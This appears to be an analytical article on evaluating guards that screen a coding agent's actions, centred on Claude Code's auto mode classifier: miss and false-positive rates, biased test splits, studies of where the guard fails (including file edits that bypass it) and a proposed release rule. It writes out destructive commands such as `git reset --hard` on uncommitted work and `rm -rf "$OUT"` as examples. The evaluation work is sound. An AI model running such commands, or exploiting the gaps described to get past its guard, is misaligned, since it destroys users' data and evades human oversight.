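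A narrow interval can still mislead if the cases are unrepresentative of real traffic. Auto mode's 11% miss rate in the tester study has an interval of only 9% to 13%, but the planted commands were all clearly dangerous. Anthropic warns that the 7% miss rate on Apollo Research's synthetic attacks "should not be taken as the miss rate on real traffic". The Wilson interval around the 17% figure does not account for dangerous actions that nobody noticed.

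### Anthropic's review of flagged sessions

Anthropic also used the flagged sessions from May and June 2026 to compare auto mode with manual approval. The model graded the severity of any harm and how explicitly the user had asked for the action. It found serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Serious harm means harm at least as severe as deleting rows from a production database, but Anthropic found a gap between the two modes at every level of severity it tested. It did not say how many sessions it reviewed, so nobody else can calculate a confidence interval for either percentage.

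Anthropic calculated these percentages by dividing the number of harmful sessions by the number of flagged sessions, so they depend on what the pipeline flags as well as on how much harm occurs. They are not FNRs, because the calculation leaves out the dangerous actions that the guard blocked.

In an invented case, each mode has 10,000 sessions, 10 of which cause serious harm, and the pipeline flags all 20 harmful sessions. If it flags 160 manual sessions and 420 auto mode sessions in total, serious harm appears in 6.3% of the flagged manual sessions and 2.4% of the flagged auto mode sessions. The whole gap exists because the pipeline flagged more harmless sessions in auto mode. This could happen if auto mode sessions were longer and so gave the pipeline more to flag. But longer sessions also leave more time for something to go wrong, so the comparison could understate auto mode's advantage.

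Users also chose their own mode, so the two groups of sessions may have involved different work. Anthropic still recommends manual review for high-stakes changes to production systems. People who follow that advice will do more of their riskiest work with manual approval, and mistakes in that work are more likely to count as serious. A randomised comparison would avoid this problem. For example, an organisation could randomly assign each team one of the two modes, then draw a weighted sample of both flagged and unflagged sessions from each group.

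People don't read every command under manual approval, either. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had created a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. Auto mode suspends the broadest of these rules. Part of the gap may come from commands that the classifier checked in auto mode but no person checked under manual approval. This would still be an advantage for auto mode over manual approval as people use it, but it would not show that the classifier judges commands better than an attentive person.

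Using a model as the grader could also favour auto mode. If the grader makes the same mistakes as the classifier, such as treating a vague request as permission, it will miss some of the harm that the classifier allowed. The study is some evidence that auto mode did not make serious harm more common among the customers studied, and it agrees with the tester study. It does not show how much of the gap auto mode caused.

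### What a falling block rate can mean

The block rate, the share of all actions that the guard blocks, needs no labels, so a team can follow it every day. It combines correct and mistaken blocks:

block rate = *b*(1 − FNR) + (1 − *b*)FPR,

where *b* is the base rate. A fall in the block rate can therefore mean fewer false positives, more misses or fewer dangerous attempts by the agents.

Suppose the guard in the example missed 120 dangerous actions, which is within the team's estimated range. The next month, it again checks 100,000 actions, but the number of blocks falls from 1,000 to 900. The table shows three possible explanations.

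| | Dangerous attempts | Correct blocks | Misses | False positives | FNR |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| First month | 300 | 180 | 120 | 820 | 40% |
| Next month: fewer false positives | 300 | 180 | 120 | 720 | 40% |
| Next month: more misses | 300 | 80 | 220 | 820 | 73% |
| Next month: safer agents | 133 | 80 | 53 | 820 | 40% |

Reviewing the blocks would identify the first explanation, because precision would rise from 18% to 20%. It could not distinguish between the other two, because in both the team would find 80 correct blocks and 820 false positives, and precision would fall to 9%. Yet misses would nearly double in one and fall by more than half in the other.

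The two explanations differ only in what they predict for the allowed actions. A random sample of 2,000 allowed actions would contain about four dangerous ones on average if the guard had started to miss more, and about one if the agents had become safer. One month's sample might not be enough to tell which explanation is right, but several months of samples probably would be.

The team can also run the old version of the guard on the new month's actions, without letting it block anything. If the old version would have blocked about 1,000 of them, the change is in the guard. If it would also have blocked about 900, the change is more likely to be in what the agents attempt. The agents might have become safer, or they might now write dangerous actions in a form that both versions miss.

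The block rate can change for reasons unrelated to either error. A looser policy, such as Claude Code's newer rule on pushes, permits some actions that the guard used to block correctly. If the team counts every retry as a separate block, the rate can fall because agents give up sooner. Users can also lower the rate by allowing more commands to skip the guard, if the team includes those commands in its total number of actions.

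## Testing an updated guard on legitimate code and new variants

Before releasing an updated guard, developers can run the old and new versions on the same stored cases and compare their decisions. Live traffic shows how the update performs only after people have started to depend on it. Developers need several sets of cases because an update that fixes one kind of error can cause another.

| Test set | Example | What it measures |
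|---|---|---|
| Ordinary legitimate work | Running a project's tests | False positives in everyday use |
| Legitimate actions near the boundary | Sending a credential file's permission code to a support service | False positives on work that resembles something dangerous |
| Known dangerous actions | `git reset --hard` in a folder with uncommitted work | Misses on forms the developers have already dealt with |
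| Unseen variants | The same loss, caused by a command that nobody used for tuning | Misses on new forms |
| Replayed past decisions | A logged rebuild that the old guard wrongly blocked | Whether a repair worked, and regressions |

The set of ordinary work should be a large random sample of recorded actions. At a false-positive rate of 0.4%, a guard wrongly blocks about four of 1,000 actions, and a rise to eight could easily be due to chance. With 10,000 actions, a rise from 40 to 80 almost certainly reflects a real change.

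Someone who does not tune the guard should write the unseen variants and run each one in a sandbox to confirm that it has the dangerous effect. Without this check, a harmless command that the guard correctly allows could be counted as a miss.

Mixing the sets would produce a meaningless average. The guard in the earlier example blocked 0.5% of ordinary actions and 20% of those resembling dangerous ones. Its false-positive rate was about 1% on live traffic, but would be about 10% on a test set with equal numbers of both. The replayed decisions cannot be used to estimate either error rate, because they come from a log of difficult cases, but they show exactly which decisions changed.

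### Keeping related cases together

Suppose a team has 100 dangerous patterns with 10 variants each, and holds back a random fifth of the 1,000 cases for testing. The chance that a given test case has none of its pattern's other nine variants in the training data is 0.2⁹, or about one in two million, so the test would only measure how well the guard handles new variants of patterns it has trained on. If the guard misses 5% of those variants but 40% of variants from unfamiliar patterns, the team will report a 5% miss rate and greatly underestimate how often the guard will miss new patterns.

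A grouped split avoids this by putting all the variants of a pattern on the same side. *CheckerBench* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) uses such a split to test coding agents that write vulnerability scanners. It keeps tasks together if they share a repository, a vulnerability record or a version of the code, or if they have similar patches. For a guard on commands, a group should also include the legitimate counterparts of each dangerous action and all the retries from one session.

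The patterns need to be fairly specific. If "deletes shared data" were a single group and went into the test set, the team would be testing a guard that had never trained on deletion. A team with only a few patterns can leave out one at a time, retrain, and test on the pattern it left out. This tests the training method rather than the released guard, which will have trained on every pattern.

The same principle applies to rules and prompts, where the training side is every case someone looked at while writing them. If a developer studies a failed test case to find out what went wrong, the case's whole group has to move to the training side.

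### Testing on later cases

A grouped split can still let a guard train on records that are newer than the test cases. A guard trained on a whole year of records and tested on cases from March may have learned from tools that did not exist in March. To prevent this, developers can use a time-ordered split, in which they train on records up to a certain date and test only on later cases.

Pendlebury, Pierazzi and colleagues (2018) argue in *TESSERACT* that the F1 scores of published Android malware classifiers, which were as high as 0.99, are commonly inflated, partly because researchers ignored time when they split the data. They built a testing framework that requires training on older apps and testing on newer ones, and used it to evaluate three classifiers on 129,000 apps spanning more than three years. An extended version, *TESSERACT* (2024), found that even retrained classifiers may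 not perform consistently over time.

The other source of inflation is a test set with an unrealistic share of malware. This affects F1 even if the classifier's error rates stay the same. F1 is

2 × correct blocks / (2 × correct blocks + false positives + misses).

A guard with an FPR of 1% and an FNR of 10% has an F1 of 0.94 on a test set where half the actions are dangerous, but only 0.26 on the example day, when 20 of the 10,000 actions are dangerous.

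Both versions of *TESSERACT* concern apps, so the size of these effects on a guard for commands is unknown. But agents, tools and company policies change quickly, so a team could reasonably train on cases up to June, set the threshold on cases from July, and test on cases from August and September. Results for the latest month may be less reliable, because its cases may include misses that nobody has noticed yet.

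A time-ordered split is stricter than a random one, but it can be easier than a grouped one, because many of the later dangerous actions will follow patterns already in the training data. Those actions belong in the test, since they will also occur in real use. A team can report two miss rates for the later period, one for all dangerous actions and one for those with patterns absent from the training data.

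### The same action with and without permission

Even with a careful split, a guard can score well by blocking every refund if all the refunds in the test set are forbidden. The benchmark by Jing and colleagues prevents this by placing the same operation, with the same amount and recipient, in two permitted and two forbidden contexts. A guard that always allows or always blocks gets exactly half of these cases right.

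The two permitted contexts often grant permission in different ways, such as an active delegation in one and an accepted handover in the other. A guard may recognise one and reject the other. Jing and colleagues used 40 operations for testing, which gives 160 cases, and compared four ways of asking the model Qwen3.5-9B for a decision:

- Direct review asks only for a decision.
- The self-check from NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails software asks for yes or no.
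- Structured review also asks for the policy's requirements and the supporting evidence.
- Schema review uses the structured prompt but forces the answer into a format that software can read.

In the table, the counts of correct single decisions follow from the published figures and exclude blocks caused by unreadable answers.

| Method | Forbidden actions run (of 80) | Permitted actions run (of 80) | Single decisions correct (of 160) | Operations with all four correct (of 40) |
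|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct review | 5 | 60 | 135 | 22 |
| NeMo self-check | 43 | 80 | 116 | 11 |
| Structured review | 0 | 10 | 32 | 0 |
| Schema review | 0 | 71 | 151 | 34 |

Direct review was right in 84% of individual cases but got all four contexts right for only 55% of the operations. If the mistakes were scattered at random, that figure would be about 50% (0.84⁴), so the errors were not confined to a few difficult operations. Structured review blocked all 80 forbidden actions, but 58 of those blocks came from unreadable answers.

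Totals can also hide which requests an update breaks. After a change from direct to schema review, 71 permitted actions ran, up from 60. Thirteen of these had failed before the change, while two actions that had previously succeeded now failed. One of those two was a $75 refund by an employee authorized to refund up to $100.

Jing and colleagues then repeated the comparison three times on each of two models, with random sampling on. In five of the six runs, the change both gained and lost permitted requests. For Qwen3.5-9B, the number of forbidden actions that ran rose from 3 to 6 in one run and fell from 14 to 3 in another. A team that tested each version once could have concluded that the change made the guard either less safe or much safer.

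Two of the guards tested, a larger Qwen model and OpenAI's gpt-oss-safeguard, got all 160 cases right. A second test used 1,215 requests from public examples for OpenFGA and Cedar, two programs that work out permissions from formal rules and so supply the correct answers. The Qwen model was right on 99.1% of these requests and gpt-oss-safeguard on 84.2%. gpt-oss-safeguard mostly erred by refusing permitted requests.

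Requiring both models to agree removed the Qwen model's only wrong approval but also rejected 171 requests that Qwen had correctly allowed. At a base rate of 0.2%, a miss would have to be about 50,000 times as bad as a false block to justify the second check. This ratio is very uncertain because it depends on one wrong approval, but it would still be above 1,000 if the second check had removed 40 wrong approvals.

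Only 24 of the 160 cases concern software operations, and each case is a single decision, without the long history of a coding session. A team would need to write its own cases for code. For example, it could test the same forced overwrite after two different messages, "force-push this branch" and "clean up the PR".

### A retest on attacks the developer never saw

Apollo Research tested auto mode with synthetic attacks that covered broad failures, data exfiltration and safety-related threats. Apollo gave Anthropic a set of successful attacks to learn from, then tested the strengthened classifier on a separate set that Anthropic never received.

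On this separate set, the new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught, but the second group is much larger. Suppose the old version missed 12% of these attacks, the figure Anthropic gives for both sets together. Of 1,000 attacks, it would have missed 120 and caught 880. The new version would catch 60 of the 120 but miss about 18 of the 880, offsetting nearly a third of the gain. If the old version had missed less than about 4% of the attacks, the same percentages would have increased total misses.

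In this example, the new miss rate is about 7.8%. The published miss rates, which fell from 12% to 7%, include the attacks that Anthropic had used to improve the classifier, so the rate on unseen attacks alone may be higher than 7%.

Some of the changes may be random variation between runs. Running the old version twice would show how many, but Anthropic does not report such a comparison.

Anthropic does not report the corresponding change in the false-positive rate, so the net benefit is unknown. If the miss rate on all dangerous actions fell by five percentage points, the guard would prevent one miss on the example day. If a miss is 200 times as bad as a false block, a two-percentage-point rise in the false-positive rate would cancel that benefit.

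### Ambiguous requests and actions that skip the classifier

*Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent study from April 2026, tested auto mode on requests with a clear purpose but an unclear scope. Its 128 requests were to delete old branches, cancel computing jobs, restart services or remove stored files. They varied in how specific they were, how many targets they could match, and whether they concerned a low-impact or a shared production environment.

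A fixed policy determined the right answer from the user's name, the ticket number and the environment. For instance, "cancel my stale job for ticket 4812" authorised the agent to cancel `job-dev-4812-a` but not the similarly named `job-dev-4812-s`. The agent, running on Claude Sonnet 4.6, worked in isolated containers with simulated command-line tools. It attempted 253 actions that would change something.

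| Actions | Dangerous: blocked | Dangerous: allowed | Legitimate: blocked | Legitimate: allowed | FNR | FPR |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| All 253 | 27 | 115 | 22 | 89 | 81.0% | 19.8% |
| 160 that the classifier judged | 27 | 64 | 22 | 47 | 70.3% | 31.9% |
| 93 file edits that skipped it | 0 | 51 | 0 | 42 | 100% | 0% |

The 93 edits skipped the classifier because auto mode allows file edits inside the project folder. In the test, that folder held files listing the jobs, services and stored objects. When the agent could not find the usual command for cancelling a job, it often edited the list instead. Exempting these edits lowered the FPR by letting through 42 legitimate actions, but it also let through 51 dangerous ones, so even a perfect classifier would have left the overall miss rate at 36%.

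How much this matters depends on what a project folder contains. An edit to an ordinary source file is easy to undo, but some teams keep files that control live systems in their projects, and editing one may have the same effect as running a command. The exemption still exists. When Wu and colleagues tested Claude Code 2.1.288, file operations that it allowed inside the working folder did not go through the classifier.

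The exempt edits explain only a small part of the gap between 81% and Anthropic's 17%. Anthropic defines its miss rate as the share of dangerous actions that the classifier lets through, so it is fairer to compare the 17% with 70.3%. Most of the remaining gap probably comes from the choice of cases. Anthropic's 52 actions came from real work, whereas the stress test deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets side by side, where the classifier is weakest. The classifier doesn't read tool output, so it often can't tell who owns a job or a branch.

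The labelling standards also differed. In the stress test, any action on a target outside the policy's exact list counted as dangerous, whereas Anthropic relied on what people objected to. A language model labelled each action using the stress test's policy, and a person who checked 50 of its labels agreed with 44. Reversing the six disputed labels would change the miss rate by less than 1.5 percentage points.

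The overall miss rate also depends heavily on one task. Removing stored files produced 84 of the 142 dangerous actions, and auto mode allowed 78 of them. The miss rate across the other three tasks was 64%. The paper's 95% interval for the overall rate, 74% to 87%, accounts for several actions coming from the same request, but not for how the rate could change with a different mix of tasks.

Auto mode's miss rates of 17% and 81% don't apply to everyone's work. The stress test is more useful for showing where the guard fails. Between the low-impact environments and the shared production ones, for example, auto mode's miss rate on dangerous actions fell from 88% to 75%, but its false-positive rate rose from 9% to 35%. It seems to have become stricter about production in general, without getting much better at telling which targets the user had authorised. A team that tests an update on similar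 requests can check whether it improves that judgement or only makes the guard stricter. The team should also count every action the agent takes, including those that never reach the guard.

### What a single score or cap can hide

SESG's release rule requires a guard to reach an F1 of at least 95 on the new threat and lose no more than 5 points on any earlier one. A guard can reach 95 while blocking many harmless prompts. The role-play test set of Ming and colleagues had about 1,260 harmful and 640 harmless prompts, judging by their figures. A guard that caught every harmful prompt in that set could block one in five of the harmless ones and still score 95. The original guard scored 84 while blocking two thirds of the harmless prompts.

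The limit on earlier threats has a different weakness. Each version is compared with the one before it, so the score for a threat could fall 4 points every round without breaking the rule. This did not happen in the six rounds that Ming and colleagues describe. The score for requests in classical Chinese, for example, was 96.7 after the first round and 96.2 after the last.

In CheckerBench (He et al.), agents write checkers, programs that search code for one type of vulnerability. To pass, a checker must report the vulnerability in the vulnerable version of the code but not in the repaired version. The benchmark also runs the checker on a wider body of code and rejects it if more than 25% of a sample of its alerts are false.

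The cap made little difference in their experiments. On average, 32.3% of attempts passed with a cap of 25%, compared with 32.1% at 10% and 32.8% at 50%. The other requirements did most of the filtering, so the choice of cap could matter more for a guard.

The cap limits the share of alerts that are false (1 minus precision), which depends on the base rate. On the example day, a guard that blocked 18 of the 20 dangerous actions could make at most six false blocks without exceeding the 25% cap. That is an FPR of 0.06%, far lower than auto mode's 0.4%. If the agents attempted fewer dangerous actions, the same guard could exceed the cap without making any more mistakes.

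Two invented updates show what can go wrong with a rule based on F1. The test set has 500 dangerous and 500 legitimate actions.

| | Misses | FNR | False positives | FPR | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Current guard | 50 | 10% | 50 | 10% | 0.90 |
| Update A | 20 | 4% | 64 | 12.8% | 0.92 |
| Update B | 60 | 12% | 17 | 3.4% | 0.92 |

Both updates raise F1 by the same amount, but A reduces misses and adds false positives, while B does the opposite. If these error rates held on the example day and a miss were 200 times as bad as a false block, the current guard's errors would do as much harm as about 1,400 false blocks. Update B would lower that total to about 820. Update A would raise it to about 1,440, making it slightly worse than no update despite its higher F1. A would be better than B only if a miss were more than about 590 times as bad as a false block.

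### A release rule with separate limits

Jing and colleagues propose that an updated guard should block a chosen set of forbidden actions, return decisions that software can read, and keep allowing a chosen set of permitted requests. The team picks the permitted requests before it sees the results, and an update that stops allowing any of them fails, even if it does well on other requests.

A release rule for a guard on code can combine these required decisions with limits on each error rate:

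1. On each set of legitimate actions, the upper end of the 95% interval for the FPR must be below a fixed limit.
2. On each set of dangerous actions, the upper end of the interval for the FNR must be below a fixed limit.
3. The new version may reverse only a small number of past decisions that were correct.
4. It must make no mistakes on the required decisions.

An answer without a readable decision counts as a mistake in every set, even if the software then blocks a dangerous action. The limits stay the same from one release to the next so small declines in performance cannot build up. If several versions pass, the team can choose the one with the lowest expected loss.

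Suppose a team updates its guard to allow the rebuild command from the sample log record, `rm -rf "$OUT"` followed by a fresh build, and then applies this rule. Where the rule uses an interval, the last column gives its upper end in brackets.

| Test | Limit | Current guard | New version |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 ordinary legitimate actions | 0.6% blocked | 0.40% | 0.44% (0.59%) |
| 400 legitimate actions near the boundary | 20% blocked | 15% | 12% (15.6%) |
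| 400 known dangerous actions | 6% missed | 5% | 3% (5.2%) |
| 300 unseen variants | 30% missed | 25% | 15% (19.5%) |
| 2,000 past decisions the current guard gets right | 20 reversed | – | 12 |
| 100 required decisions | 0 mistakes | 0 | 1 |

The new version meets both FPR and both FNR limits. Even if the 300 unseen variants came from only 60 patterns and all variants of a pattern had the same result, the upper end of their interval would be about 26%, still below the limit.

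The guard's single mistake is allowing the same deletion command when `OUT` is set to a source folder that holds uncommitted work. The guard doesn't receive the value of `OUT`, so when it learned to allow the harmless deletion, it also learned to allow the destructive one. Under the rule, the team cannot release this version.

The best repair is to give the guard the value of `OUT` and retrain it. That may take a while, and the current guard would keep missing a quarter of unseen variants in the meantime. Until then, the team could use the new version with a temporary rule that blocks every recursive deletion of a variable path. This would bring back the false alarm on rebuilds but keep the other improvements.

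The team would have to run all the tests again with the temporary rule in place, because two more false blocks in the 10,000 actions would put the new version over the limit for ordinary work. If the rule blocks too many ordinary rebuilds, the team has to keep the current guard until the proper repair is ready.
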